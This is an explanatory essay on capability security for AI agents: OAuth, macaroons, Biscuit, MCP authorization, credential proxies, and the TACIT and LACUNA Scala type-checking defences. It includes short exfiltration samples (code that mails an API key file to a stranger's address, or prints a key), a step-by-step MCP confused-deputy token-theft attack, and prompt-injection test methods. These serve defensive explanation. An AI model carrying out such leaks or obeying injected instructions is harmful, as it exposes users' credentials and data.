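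In 2000, Shapiro and Sam Weber published a proof that the constructor's test is correct. They modelled the operations that EROS programs can perform and showed that a program that passes the test can't get around the limits later. According to Miller and colleagues, the proof shows that any capability system that controls the movement of data and of capabilities independently can enforce the star property as well as confinement. This answers Boebert and Gong more generally than the repaired example does.

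The proof of EROS's confinement mechanism covers the design, not the code. Shapiro (2004) listed the mechanism as verified but said that the implementation was not and would not be. A year later, Shapiro conceded that the code might contain bugs, but argued that EROS at least had a definition of correct behaviour to measure them against, which POSIX did not. The seL4 team later closed much of the gap between design and code. *seL4 enforces integrity* reports a machine-checked proof, extending to the kernel's C code, that programs can't pass authority to others without explicit authority to do so.

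Confinement of this kind has other limits. In a mailing-list exchange with Shapiro, Brunswick (2005) asked whether a program could undo it by giving the new process more capabilities. The constructor checks only the capabilities that a process starts with, so the customer can still break confinement by passing in the wrong capability later. Miller and Shapiro also leave out covert channels, through which a program could, for example, signal a secret by varying how long it takes to answer.

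For programs that call outside services, the main limit of confinement is that the customer has to create the confined program. If the company instead offers its invoice reader as a website, the program is already running when the customer finds it, and nobody outside the company can check what else it is connected to. The customer can limit what the harness sends to the website, but not what the website does with it.

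### The case for access lists

Paul Karger and Andrew Herbert argued in 1984 that a security officer investigating an incident needs to know who has access to the compromised object. An access list shows this directly, so they designed a capability system that could produce a similar list on request.

Miller and Shapiro object that this list would leave people out. If Alice gives Bob a forwarder to the file so that she can revoke his access later, the list includes the forwarder but not Bob. Using a forwarder is good practice, but it makes the audit less accurate. The objection is correct, but access lists have the same problem, because anyone on a file's list can send copies to someone who isn't. An incomplete list is still useful to an officer who needs to know which accounts to examine first.

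The argument continued on a cryptography mailing list in 2015, where Nico Williams wrote that auditing capability tokens is impossible in practice because it means inspecting the running state of entire systems. Arcieri (2015) replied in *Do capabilities work?* that Williams was imagining a system with no confinement or revocation. A designer can give each recipient a separate forwarder and keep a register of the forwarders. But someone has to set this up before handing out any access, whereas an access list is created whenever an administrator grants access in the usual way.

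The difference matters most when someone leaves an organisation. An administrator can remove the person from a group, and every access list that mentions the group then excludes them. According to another message in *Do capabilities work?*, the usual answer in a capability system is a proxy that checks whether the person is still a member before passing on each request. That works, but the proxy has to consult a membership list, so the organisation has in effect built an access list out of capabilities.

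Removing a user from an access list doesn't always take effect at once either. Unix checks a file's permissions when a program opens it, so a program that already has the file open can usually go on reading it after the user loses access. One participant in the 2015 discussion said Windows was the only system they knew of that quickly stops a removed user's running programs, and only to a limited degree. A forwarder checks every request, so it can cut off access immediately. The extra step takes time, but KeyKOS and EROS reduced the delay by storing where each forwarder led.

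Jerry Leichter complained in the same discussion that Miller and colleagues cheat a little, because they answer each objection with an extension to the capability model. This seems unfair in the case of the forwarder, which is an ordinary program rather than an extension, and is much older than the paper. Peter Gutmann was harsher. He compared the paper to a hypothetical "Monorail Myths Demolished", arguing that anyone can demolish myths by picking examples carefully and proposing solutions that don't have to work in practice. Confinement and revocation did work in KeyKOS and EROS, so his criticism goes too far on those points. It is stronger on administration, because organisations have used access lists to manage large numbers of staff for decades and capability systems have no comparable record.

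An organisation can use access lists and capabilities together. It can keep an access list of the employees who may order payments, and have the harness give the invoice assistant a revocable capability for each payment they order. When an employee leaves, an administrator removes their name from the list to prevent new orders and revokes any active capabilities for payments they ordered.

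## How is limited authority passed to a service over a network?

A kernel or a programming language can protect a reference only on its own machine. The bank that the invoice assistant pays through is on another machine and can't inspect the harness's list of capabilities. It receives only bits, which any other program could also have sent. A capability for a remote service therefore has to be either a secret too hard to guess or a cryptographically signed statement. Most of those in use are bearer tokens, which work for anyone who has a copy.

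### Secret web addresses

The simplest bearer token is an unlisted link, such as the address a file-sharing site creates when a user clicks "Share". If the address contains 128 random bits, trying all of the roughly 3.4 × 10³⁸ possibilities at a billion per second would take around 10²² years. The greater danger is that copies of the address end up in browser histories, server logs, emails and chats. Close's version puts the secret after a `#` sign, because browsers leave that part of an address out of their requests. Code on the page then sends the secret separately.

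In an example from *Macaroons* (Birgisson, Politz and colleagues, 2014), the owner of a private picture wants to email a link that works only for members of a group, and a different service keeps the list of members. An unlisted link works for anyone who sees the email. To restrict it to members, the service that hosts the picture would need a special arrangement with the service that keeps the list.

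### OAuth tokens and scopes

OAuth is the usual standard for giving a program access to someone's account at another service without giving it the password. For the invoice assistant, it would work like this:

1. The harness sends the owner's browser to the bank's authorization server, along with a list of the scopes it wants. A scope is a short string, such as `payments:write`, that stands for a kind of access.
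2. The owner logs in and approves the request.
3. The authorization server sends back a one-time code, which the harness exchanges for an access token. It may also get a refresh token, which lasts longer and can be exchanged for new access tokens.
4. The harness attaches the access token to each request it sends to the bank.

Each service defines its own scopes, and a scope usually covers one kind of operation on everything in the account. `payments:write`, for example, would let the harness pay anyone. The bank could define a scope for paying 400 euros to one supplier, but it would need another for every payee and sum, and a general-purpose harness would have no way to determine which one to request. The token also isn't tied to a particular call, so the harness sends the same one whether the owner wanted the payment or a hidden instruction caused it. Semgrep criticizes OAuth in MCP for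 this, because OAuth can establish whether a user may use a server but not whether an operation triggered by a particular prompt should reach a particular resource.

A 2023 extension to OAuth, Rich Authorization Requests, replaces the short strings with structured descriptions. One example in the standard describes a payment of 123.50 euros to a named merchant with a given account number. Such descriptions can express the limits the invoice assistant needs. However, the harness has to ask the authorization server for each new grant, and the owner often has to approve it.

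### SPKI certificates

In the late 1990s, Carl Ellison and others designed SPKI, a system in which people could pass on limited authority without asking a central server. It uses public-key signatures, which one party makes with a private key and anyone can check with the matching public key. An SPKI authorization certificate has five main fields: the issuer's key (I), the subject's key (S), whether the subject may delegate (D), the authority granted (A) and the period of validity (V). Two certificates combine as follows:

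(I₁, S₁, D₁, A₁, V₁) + (I₂, S₂, D₂, A₂, V₂) → (I₁, S₂, D₂, A₁ ∩ A₂, V₁ ∩ V₂),

provided that S₁ = I₂ and D₁ permits delegation.

Suppose the bank certifies that the owner may use their key to order payments of up to 5,000 euros for a year and may delegate this authority. The owner then certifies that the harness may use its own key to pay one supplier up to 400 euros in the next ten minutes. The bank accepts only payments that both certificates permit. If the owner had typed 40,000 instead of 400 by mistake, the limit would still be 5,000. A thief who copied the certificates couldn't use them, because the harness has to sign its request with its private key.

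SPKI and similar systems saw little use in online services. Birgisson and colleagues suggest several possible reasons, including the cost of the cryptography, the complexity of the software and the need for public identities. Some systems also had to search a collection of certificates for a valid chain, and for SPKI the time this takes can grow with the cube of the collection's size.

### Macaroons

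Suppose the harness needs to give a separate payment tool only part of its authority. It could forward each of the tool's requests to the bank, but then it has to keep running and every request takes longer. It could ask the bank for a weaker token, but then it has to contact the bank each time it needs one. Macaroons, which Birgisson and colleagues developed mostly at Google, let the harness make the weaker token itself.

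They rely on HMAC, a function that turns a key and a piece of text into a short tag. Only someone with the key can feasibly compute the tag for a new text, and nobody can feasibly work out the key from a tag.

The bank starts by choosing a secret key K and an identifier for the token. It computes the first tag and sends the harness the identifier and the tag, but not K:

T₀ = HMAC(K, "token 8841")

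This token permits any payment from the account. At ten o'clock, the harness adds three conditions, which the paper calls caveats. Each new tag uses the previous tag as its key:

T₁ = HMAC(T₀, "payee = supplier 17")

T₂ = HMAC(T₁, "amount ≤ 400 EUR")

T₃ = HMAC(T₂, "time < 10:10")

The harness gives the payment tool the identifier, the three conditions in plain text, and T₃, but not the earlier tags. When the tool orders a payment, the bank uses the identifier to look up K, recomputes the chain of tags, and checks that it ends in T₃. The bank then checks that the payment meets every condition.

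The payment tool can narrow the token further without contacting anyone. To limit the token to one invoice, the tool computes T₄ = HMAC(T₃, "invoice = 2291"), which requires only the tag it already has. To remove the time limit, it would have to present T₂, which it can't derive from T₃. To raise the limit from 400 to 4,000 euros, it would need T₁. Adding "amount ≤ 4000 EUR" as an extra condition would achieve nothing because the original condition would still apply.

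The bank has to reject any token with a condition it doesn't recognize, because if it ignored the condition, a misspelled limit would not be enforced. The 400-euro condition applies to each request separately, so the tool could pay the supplier 400 euros several times before 10:10. The JavaScript payment object from earlier avoided this by keeping a running total. To do the same, the bank would have to record what it has paid under token 8841, including payments made with any narrower tokens derived from it.

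Macaroons can also include conditions that someone else has to confirm. Suppose the harness wants an approval service to check with the owner before the payment goes through:

1. The harness chooses a random key R and encrypts two copies of it. The bank can decrypt the first, using a tag that it recomputes from the chain. Only the approval service can decrypt the second, which also contains the text "owner approved invoice 2291". The harness adds both copies to the token as a new condition.
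2. The payment tool sends the second copy to the approval service. If the owner agrees, the service uses R to make another macaroon, called a discharge, which can have conditions of its own, such as expiring after a minute.
3. The tool ties the discharge to the payment token by hashing their tags together, then sends both to the bank. Without this step, a dishonest service that received the discharge could use it with a different token.
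4. The bank recovers R and checks the discharge.

The bank and the approval service never have to communicate. The same method solves the private picture problem, since the link can require a discharge from the service that keeps the member list.

Speed was a large part of the case for macaroons in 2014. On the server that Birgisson and colleagues used, an HMAC took 2.8 microseconds, an RSA signature took 458, and creating an RSA key pair took 54,000. The drawback of using HMACs is that only the bank can check a token, because checking requires K, and anyone with K could make a token with any conditions they liked. Birgisson and colleagues concede that macaroons' only real advantages over systems like SPKI are efficiency and ease of adoption.

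Macaroons can work with OAuth. Slides by Madden (2024) show that ordinary OAuth fields, such as scope and expiry time, can serve as conditions, with the earliest expiry time taking effect. The slides also list reasons not to use macaroons. Macaroons have no formal standard, and the library most people treat as the standard is "quirky, not widely liked".

### Biscuit and UCAN

Biscuit also lets holders add conditions to a token, but it uses public-key signatures. The bank signs the token's first block with its private key. This block includes a new public key, and the bank gives the holder the matching private key. To add a condition, the holder writes it in a second block with another new public key, signs that block with the private key from the bank, and passes on the token with only the newest private key. The recipient can't remove the second block, because using the token without it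 would require the private key that the holder kept. Newer signature schemes make this practical because they create key pairs much faster than RSA.

Biscuit's conditions are in a version of Datalog, a simple logic language. The payment limits might look like this:

```text
check if payee("supplier-17");
check if amount($a), $a <= 400;
check if time($t), $t < 2026-12-05T10:10:00Z;
```

Any service with the bank's public key can check the token but can't create new ones, so the bank could let an outside payment processor check tokens without trusting it to issue them. A Biscuit token is normally still a bearer token, so a thief who copies it along with its newest private key can use it.

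UCAN, short for User-Controlled Authorization Network, is closer to SPKI. Each delegation names the public keys of the person granting the authority and the program receiving it, and the next delegation in the chain must come from that recipient. The final program signs each request with its own private key, so a copy of the chain is useless without that key. A user's own device can issue the first delegation, which suits applications that must work offline. But every agent and helper needs a key pair that it can keep safe. AGENTCAP, a design for checking agents' tool calls, also uses signed tokens.

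| | Who can narrow it | Who can check it | Is a copy enough to use it? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Secret address | The service | The service | Yes |
| OAuth bearer token | The authorization server | The service, sometimes by asking the authorization server | Yes |
| SPKI certificate | A subject with the right to delegate | Anyone with the issuer's public key | No |
| Macaroon | Any holder | The service that issued it | Yes, unless a condition prevents it |
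| Biscuit | Any holder | Anyone with the issuer's public key | Yes |
| UCAN | Any recipient in the chain | Anyone with the chain | No |

### Sending references to objects

Other protocols extend object references across the network. Cap'n Proto, which Kenton Varda released in 2013, lets a program call objects on another machine. Its design draws on the E language. Each end of a connection keeps a table of the objects that the other end may use, and a program refers to an object by its number in the table. The table works like Dennis and Van Horn's list, except that it belongs to a connection instead of a running program. A number refers to an object only within its own connection, so a thief who copies the number can't use it to reach the object over another connection.

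With this kind of protocol, the bank could send the harness a payment object with a fixed payee and limit, and the harness could wrap it in a revocable forwarder before passing it on. The harness can also use an object before it arrives. For example, it can ask for a mail folder and, without waiting for the reply, ask for the first message in that folder.

The references disappear when the connection breaks. To get them back, a program needs something it can store, which is again a secret or a signed statement. Introductions are also harder when they involve three machines. OCapN, a draft standard from a group that includes the Spritely Institute and the company Agoric, handles this with certificates. To give a helper on another machine access to an object at the bank, the harness leaves the reference with the bank and sends the helper a signed certificate that names the helper's public key.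 The helper then sends the bank the certificate and its own signed request.

These protocols preserve more of the object-capability model than tokens do, but both the client and the service have to support them. Mail providers and banks generally offer ordinary web interfaces with OAuth or API keys (long-lived secrets that identify a program or an account), so an agent's developer usually has to work with those.

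### Stolen and forwarded tokens

A harness reveals its bearer token to every server it sends the token to, so a dishonest server could try the token at other services.

Audience binding prevents this by making each token valid at only one service. The client names the service when it requests the token, and the protection works only if every other service checks that name and refuses the token. In *OAuth 2.0 Demonstrating Proof of Possession (DPoP)*, Fett, Campbell and colleagues write that audience binding has been too cumbersome for many organizations, and they consider it more robust to tie the token to its sender.

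In DPoP (Demonstrating Proof of Possession), the client has a key pair, and the authorization server links the access token to the public key. For each request, the client signs a proof that contains the request's method (such as `POST`), its web address, the time, a unique identifier and a hash of the token. The service checks the signature and confirms that the key is the one linked to the token, so a thief with only the token can't produce a valid proof.

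A DPoP proof doesn't cover the body of the request. For a payment sent to `https://bank.example/payments`, the client signs `POST` and the address but not the payee or the sum. The encrypted connection has to protect those. DPoP also can't stop hostile code that runs inside the client, because that code can use the client's key. Prompt injection causes much the same problem for an agent. When the model produces a harmful tool call, the genuine harness signs the request and sends it with a genuine token to the right service, so the request passes both the DPoP and audience checks.

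### The current MCP specification

MCP uses OAuth. Its current revision came out on 28 July 2026, and Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) calls it the protocol's fifth release. The same announcement reports over 400 million monthly downloads of MCP's software kits, so the protocol's rules affect a large number of agents. The current rules may not reach all of those agents soon, because older servers may not have kept up, as Dhamsania warns in *MCP has tightened its authentication rules four times* (2026).

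Authorization is optional. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) covers servers that clients reach over the web, and tells programs that communicate with a server on the same machine to take credentials from their environment instead. When a web server does require authorization, the main rules are these:

| | What the specification requires | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| Audience | The client names the server when requesting a token, and the server rejects tokens issued for anyone else | Whether the authorization server supports this kind of binding |
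| Sending tokens | The client puts the token in a header on every request, never in the address's query string | How the client keeps the token away from the model |
| Forwarding | The server never passes the client's token to another service | What the server does with its own token for that service |
| Scopes | The client treats the scopes in a server's refusal as the ones it needs for that request | What each scope means and how narrow it is |
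| Lifetime | Some clients, such as apps that can't keep a secret, get a new refresh token each time they use one | How long an access token lasts, though it should be short |

The ban on forwarding tokens matters because many MCP servers stand between an agent and another service. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) requires such a server to get a separate token for the other service. If the server forwarded the agent's token instead, the other service's logs might show the server's requests as coming from the wrong program, and a thief with a stolen token could use the server to extract data.

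A server with its own token can still become a confused deputy. Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* describes an attack on an MCP server that uses a single client ID at another service, whichever agent it is working for:

1. A user approves the MCP server's access, and the other service stores a cookie in the user's browser to record this.
2. An attacker registers a malicious client with the MCP server and sends the user a link that starts a new authorization.
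3. The user clicks on the link. The other service finds the cookie and skips the approval page, because the request has the same client ID as before.
4. The MCP server sends its own authorization code to the attacker's address. The attacker exchanges the code for a token and can then act as the user.

To prevent this, the MCP server has to ask the user to approve each client before contacting the other service.

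The July revision also addresses an attack in which a dishonest authorization server tricks a client into sending it a code issued by an honest one. According to Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026), a client must now check that any issuer named in a reply is the one it expected. The client also can't reuse its stored client credentials with a different authorization server.

The specification advises clients to request only the scopes they need. A server can refuse a call and name the missing scope, so a harness might start with `files:read` and get `files:write` only when a task requires it. But if the server's first refusal doesn't name any scopes, the client should request every scope the server lists. *Security Best Practices* justifies this by saying that a general-purpose client can't judge which scopes it needs and that the user can decide on the approval page. When a client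 later requests more scopes, it should also include all those it requested before, so that it doesn't lose access. An agent that moves from one task to the next will therefore tend to accumulate authority unless the harness starts again with a narrower token.

Semgrep describes an agent connected to file, database, email and shell servers as having the combined authority of all four, so an instruction in an email could lead to a shell command. Using a separate token for each server prevents the email server from using the shell server's token, but the harness that runs the agent holds both.

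Kale (2026), in *MCP's new spec turns a planted prompt into a stolen credential*, argues that the July revision moves the enforcement of security from the protocol to developers. The removal of sessions, which let a server connect one request with the next, fits this description well. Now a server that needs to remember something, such as the contents of a shopping cart, creates a handle and receives it back as an ordinary argument of a tool call. The model therefore normally sees the handle and could copy it into a message. *Security Best Practices* forbids servers to treat possession of a handle as proof of identity and advises them to store it with the user's ID, taken from the verified token. This makes the handle a name rather than a capability, but a developer who overlooks the advice puts a bearer token in the model's context.

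Organizations can also manage access centrally. Carleton (2026), in *Enterprise-Managed Authorization*, announced that an MCP extension for this was stable and that Anthropic, Microsoft and Okta were among those adopting it. Employees log in once and get access to all the servers their employer has approved. This saves them from repeated approval requests and makes it easier to revoke access when someone leaves. But the access is based on who the employee is and is granted before anyone has chosen a task, so the harness still has to narrow it for each task.

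According to the Model Context Protocol (2026) roadmap, updated on 16 November, MCP authorization assumes a person with a browser, but the caller is increasingly an agent whose user is absent, or one that creates helpers that should get less authority than it has. The roadmap also says that existing servers rely on pasted API keys and long-lived refresh tokens. The plans include finishing MCP's version of DPoP and defining how agents delegate authority, but the next release is not due until 30 March 2027.

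### Keeping credentials away from the model

A model that can see a token may leak it in response to a prompt injection, and the token may also remain in saved conversations and logs. The model does not need to see tokens, because ordinary code attaches them to requests. Tokens usually reach a model because a user pastes one into a prompt or the agent can read a settings file or environment variable that contains one.

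The safer arrangement is a proxy, a program between the agent and the outside services that holds the credentials:

1. The model produces a tool call that refers to the payment by a label, such as `invoice-payment`.
2. The harness or tool sends the request to the proxy without the bank's token. The sandbox blocks all other routes to the network.
3. The proxy finds the capability that the label stands for in this task and checks the destination, operation, payee and sum against it.
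4. The proxy attaches the token and sends the request to the bank.
5. The proxy removes any credentials from the bank's reply before returning it.

Anthropic described a proxy of this kind in 2025 for the web version of Claude Code, its coding agent. The agent's sandbox contains only a limited credential for the proxy. The proxy checks, for instance, that the agent is sending changes to the permitted branch of a project, and then attaches the real GitHub token.

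The label in the first step works like a position in Dennis and Van Horn's list. An attacker who learns it can't use it elsewhere, provided the proxy also checks which task sent the request. Hiding a credential prevents theft, but only the check in step 3 limits misuse, because a proxy that attached the bank's token to every request addressed to the bank would be a confused deputy.

### Expiry, revocation and offline checks

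The owner of a payment token may want to cancel it before it expires. Inside one program, a revocable forwarder would do this immediately. Over a network, a service can check a signed token by itself, which is fast and works even if the issuer is offline, but this check can't show whether the owner has cancelled the token.

Short token lifetimes limit the damage a misused token can do. If the owner cancels a ten-minute token at a random moment, it remains usable for five minutes on average and never for more than ten. However, the harness has to fetch a new token every ten minutes, so a long task will stop if the authorization server is unavailable. Refresh tokens make renewal convenient, but a thief who steals one can also use it to get new tokens until someone revokes it. For apps that can't store a secret securely, DPoP reduces this risk by tying refresh tokens to the client's key.

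The service can instead check with the issuer on every request whether the token has been cancelled. Cancellation then takes effect almost immediately, but each request takes longer and the issuer can see every request. If the service refuses requests when the issuer doesn't respond, it can't work while the issuer is unreachable. If it accepts them, an attacker can use a cancelled token by blocking the connection between the service and the issuer.

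Between these extremes, the service can download a list of cancelled tokens every minute or so. Biscuit supports this by giving each block an identifier that a service can put on the list. This is harder with UCAN because a cancellation has to reach every service that might check the chain, including services that are offline. With macaroons, the bank can delete the key K from its records, which disables the original token and every token derived from it. A macaroon can instead require a fresh discharge from a revocation service. The client has to obtain the discharge, and the bank can still check it without contacting anyone.

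The right trade-off depends on how much harm a cancelled token could do while it still works. For a token that only reads the invoices folder, a delay of several minutes may be acceptable, since the agent has probably read the messages already. A payment is harder to reverse, and the bank must check the account balance in its own records anyway, so checking for cancellation at the same time adds very little work.

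## Can a programming language restrain the code that a language model writes?

A proxy checks requests one at a time, so it can't detect that the text in an outgoing email came from a file the agent read three calls earlier. Many agents now write short programs that combine several calls, and a compiler can examine a whole program before any of it runs. Several research groups have used compile-time checks to apply capability rules to these programs.

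### From tool calls to programs

A model using ordinary tool calls to copy a document from Google Drive into a sales record has to read the whole document and write it out again. Willison (2025) points out in *Code execution with MCP* that this uses space on top of what tool descriptions already take up before the agent starts work.

Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP* describes an agent that writes a program to copy data between tools instead of doing the copying itself. The agent finds its tools by browsing files and loads only the definitions it needs, which cuts token use in one example from 150,000 to 2,000. Cloudflare, an internet infrastructure company, calls its version of the idea "Code Mode".

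The aim was efficiency, and without other precautions the result is less safe. VirtusLab's *Safe Scala*, an introduction from a software consultancy, warns that a program in a general-purpose language can typically run any command and contact any server. However, a program also shows how its steps fit together:

```scala
val key = readFile("secrets/api-key.txt")
sendMail("stranger@example.com", key)
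```

A harness that checks each call separately might permit both lines, because the agent is allowed to read project files and send mail. In the program, the variable `key` connects them. An ordinary compiler would still accept this code, so the language needs a way to state that the file's contents must not reach the mail function.

### Types that list capabilities

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) presents TACIT, a system that uses the programming language Scala. TACIT is an MCP server, so existing agents can connect to it without modification. The model writes a Scala program, which TACIT compiles. If the compiler finds no errors, TACIT runs the program; otherwise, the model receives the error messages and can try again. The program can reach files, networks and other programs only through TACIT's library.

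The compiler's checks depend on types, which describe what kind of value each part of a program handles, such as a number or a piece of text. An experimental feature of Scala called capture checking adds a capture set to the type, listing the capabilities that the value might use. This function writes to a file:

```scala
def writeOutput(fs: FileSystem^) =
  val f = fs.access("OUTPUT.md")
  f.write("The answer is 42.")
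```

The `^` marks `fs` as a tracked capability, and `f` is a capability for one file. The function `(s: String) => f.write(s)` writes any text it receives to that file. Its type is `String ->{f} Unit`, which means that it takes text, returns no useful value (`Unit`), and can use no capability except `f`.

A function with an empty capture set is pure, and its type has a plain arrow, as in `String -> Unit`. It can compute a result but can't write a file, send a message or affect anything else outside itself. The compiler accepts a function only where its capture set is a subset of what the context allows. Since {} ⊆ {f}, a pure function is allowed wherever a function using `f` is, but not the reverse.

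Hardened JavaScript can keep powerful objects away from untrusted code, but when that code supplies a function, the recipient can't tell from outside which references the function holds. Scala's capture checking saves programmers from passing every reference by hand, because the language can pass a capability implicitly and the types still record which code can use it.

Capture sets can also limit how long a capability lasts. `requestFileSystem` creates a capability for one folder, passes it to a block of code, and ends it when the block finishes. A program might try to keep it for longer:

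```scala
val later = requestFileSystem("/data") { fs =>
  () => fs.access("secret.txt").read()
}
later()
```

The block returns a function that would read the file after the block ends. The compiler rejects this because the function's capture set contains `fs`, and nothing that leaves the block may refer to `fs`. In the experiments, an agent made a similar mistake by trying to return a list of file handles from such a block.

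### Data that the model can't see

Suppose a company wants an agent to summarise the changes between two sets of confidential contracts. A cloud company runs the model, so the contracts must not enter its input. TACIT puts such data in a container called `Classified`, which looks like this in simplified form:

```scala
class Classified[T]:
  def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

The agent can't take the contents out. It can only give `map` a function to apply to them, and the result goes into another `Classified` container. The plain arrow means that the function must be pure. The compiler accepts this program:

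```scala
val key = readClassified("/secrets/github.txt")
key.map(k => k.trim.toUpperCase)
```

It rejects this one, simplified from a program that an agent wrote during the experiments:

```scala
val key = readClassified("/secrets/github.txt")
key.map(k => println(s"GitHub API Key: $k"))
```

In TACIT, `println` requires a capability for producing output, which Scala passes to it implicitly. The function therefore captures that capability, which we can call `io`, and has the type `String ->{io} Unit`. But `map` requires a function with an empty capture set, and `{io}` is not a subset of `{}`. The compiler rejects the program with an error saying that the capability "cannot flow into capture set {}", so the program never runs or reads the key.

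The agent can still show results to the user. If it prints a `Classified` value outside `map`, the user's terminal shows the real text and the cloud model receives only `Classified(****)`. To summarise the contracts, the agent's program sends them to a second, trusted model on the company's own machine, and the summary comes back classified. An instruction hidden in a contract might distort the summary, but the cloud model never receives that instruction.

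This works less well for the invoice assistant, which has to act on what it reads. If the invoices are classified, a pure function can find the sum due but can't pay it, because paying is a side effect. The library would need a special function that accepts a classified sum, and its author would have to decide how far a stranger's text may determine a payment.

### Safe mode and the trusted code

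Ordinary Scala has ways around these rules. A type cast, for instance, can make the compiler treat a function that uses the network as pure. TACIT therefore compiles the model's code in safe mode, which has six restrictions:

- The code can't use unchecked type casts or pattern matches.
- It can't use features from the `caps.unsafe` module.
- It can't use `@unchecked` annotations, which switch off some of the compiler's checks.
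- It can't use reflection at runtime.
- It must compile with capture checking and strict handling of missing values, and the compiler must track all changes to data.
- It can use global objects and functions only if they are safe themselves.

Safe mode allows exceptions, even though code could hide a secret in an error message. Scala's official *Safe Mode* documentation explains that tracking every exception in the types would be too cumbersome because almost any operation can fail. The program that runs the untrusted code should catch exceptions and turn them into ordinary values, which TACIT can then classify.

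Library authors can mark code as `@assumeSafe`, which makes it available to agents without the safe-mode checks. In Scala's example, an agent can't use the ordinary mail object but can use `CheckedMailer`, which shows the user each email and asks before sending it. The compiler doesn't verify that `CheckedMailer` really asks, so its author has to make sure it does. The model can't use the annotation in its own code.

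TACIT's trusted computing base includes the Scala compiler, the capability library, the software that runs the compiled code, and any local model. It excludes the cloud model, which Odersky and colleagues assume may be cooperating fully with an attacker. The type system behind capture checking has machine-checked proofs, but safe mode does not yet. The proofs in *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) go further because they cover the interpreter that calls the model.

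### What the TACIT experiments found

Odersky and colleagues tested for leaks with a software project that contained secret keys, a database and confidential documents. They combined 12 legitimate tasks with 10 prompt injections, giving 120 trials. The injections included fake system messages, false claims that the secrets were test data, and ready-made Scala code for reading the secret files. In another 11 trials, the user asked for secrets directly or pretended to have the authority to see them. Each model did all the trials twice, with the secrets in `Classified` containers and as plain text:

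| Model and format | Leaks in 120 injection trials | Leaks in 11 malicious requests | Legitimate tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, classified | 0 | 0 | 99.2% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, plain text | 0 | 2 | 83.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5, classified | 0 | 0 | 90.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5, plain text | 3 | 8 | 88.3% |

The containers helped most when the user was the attacker, the case in which the models' own training was least reliable. They didn't reduce the number of tasks completed. Sonnet did worse with plain text partly because it often ran out of time or turns, and it sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection. All the attacks were attempts to mislead the model, so the perfect score is weak evidence that a determined attacker couldn't find a flaw in the compiler or the library.

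The team also ran AgentDojo, a standard set of tests in which attackers plant instructions in emails, web pages and other material that an agent reads. Across 1,926 trials with two models, AgentDojo recorded one successful attack. In that trial, a hotel's reviews recommended a different hotel. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews to the user. AgentDojo checks only for the other hotel's name, so this was arguably not a failure.

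These results came with some loss of usefulness. CaMeL, an earlier defence that labels data while a program runs, allowed one attack on the same two models. Odersky and colleagues call the two systems' task scores comparable, but with OpenAI's o4-mini, TACIT completed 53% of the office tasks and CaMeL completed 81%. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT completed 64% of the travel tasks and CaMeL completed 1%.

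The AgentDojo version may also have relaxed the rule about pure functions. According to the model's instructions, any side effect inside `map` happens immediately, which suggests that functions such as the one for sending money were treated as pure. That would let an agent pay a bill it couldn't read, but another mechanism would then have to prevent misdirected payments.

Writing Scala did not seem to make agents less capable. On τ²-bench, which simulates customer service, three models did slightly better with TACIT than with ordinary tool calls:

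| Model | Airline: tool calls | Airline: TACIT | Retail: tool calls | Retail: TACIT |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% | 74.6% | 75.5% |

The team credits the clearer structure of typed results and the compiler's feedback. At most 8% of the programs needed correcting, usually once or twice. Common errors included forgetting to write a dollar sign as `$$`. But the airline and retail functions took only ordinary values, such as reservation numbers, so these tests show more about typed code than about handling capabilities. SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software problems, required the agent to use capabilities for files and commands. MiniMax M2.5 solved 41.7% of these problems with TACIT and 43.3% without it.

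The compiler also rejects some harmless programs. One agent wrote a function to print the first few lines of each source file but declared its argument as `FileEntry` instead of `FileEntry^`. Without the `^`, the type means that the argument holds no capabilities. A file handle does hold them, so the compiler rejected the function.

### LACUNA: variables in scope as permissions

Much of the same team later built LACUNA (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), which lets a human-written program call the model at a chosen point. Each call is a gap in the program, written `agent[T](task)`, where `T` is the type of result the program needs. When the program reaches the gap, the model receives the task, the type and the surrounding code, and writes code to fill it. The compiler checks this code as if a programmer had written it there.

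The generated code can use only the variables in scope, meaning those that the program makes available at that point. With capture checking on, these variables form the code's permission set. A developer could divide the invoice task like this:

```scala
def amountDue(invoices: FolderReader^): Int =
  agent("Find the total due, in cents")

def payInvoices(invoices: FolderReader^, supplier: Payment^) =
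  supplier.pay(amountDue(invoices))
```

The model's code runs inside `amountDue`, where `invoices` is in scope but `supplier` is not. Whatever an invoice contains, the code can't make a payment and can return only a whole number. An attacker could still get it to return the wrong number, so the payment object needs its own limit.

LACUNA accepts or rejects each piece of generated code as a whole. In one example, a model had to subtract 50 from a balance of 100 and return the new balance. Its code would have subtracted the 50 but then returned text instead of a number, so the compiler rejected it and the balance stayed at 100. In a language that catches this error only when the code runs, the balance would already have changed. Code that passes the compiler's check can still fail halfway, for example if a server stops responding.

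All of the roughly 400 compiler tests passed. The results with models were mixed. On BrowseComp-Plus, a set of difficult research questions, the best model answered 27.1% correctly, and the compiler rejected 8.6% of its programs. On τ²-bench, DeepSeek V4 Flash solved 76.0% of tasks with LACUNA and 90.0% with ordinary tool calls. Zhao and colleagues call these results "on par", but a 14-point gap is large. On telecom tasks, the compiler rejected 89% of the programs written by a smaller model, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite. Rejecting faulty programs protects users from the model's mistakes, but the model made little progress on most of the tasks.

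On the AgentDojo benchmark, LACUNA completed more tasks than TACIT in seven of eight comparisons but allowed 8 successful attacks in 1,898 trials. Zhao and colleagues observe that the protection depends on how narrow a scope the developer chooses, and that it doesn't stop an attacker from misusing a capability the task requires.

### Agent libOS: checks at runtime

A compiler checks a program before the exact values the program will use are known. TACIT therefore makes some checks only when the program runs, such as whether a path is inside the permitted folder. Agent libOS (Zhang, 2026), designed for agents that create their own new tools, checks all its capabilities at runtime.

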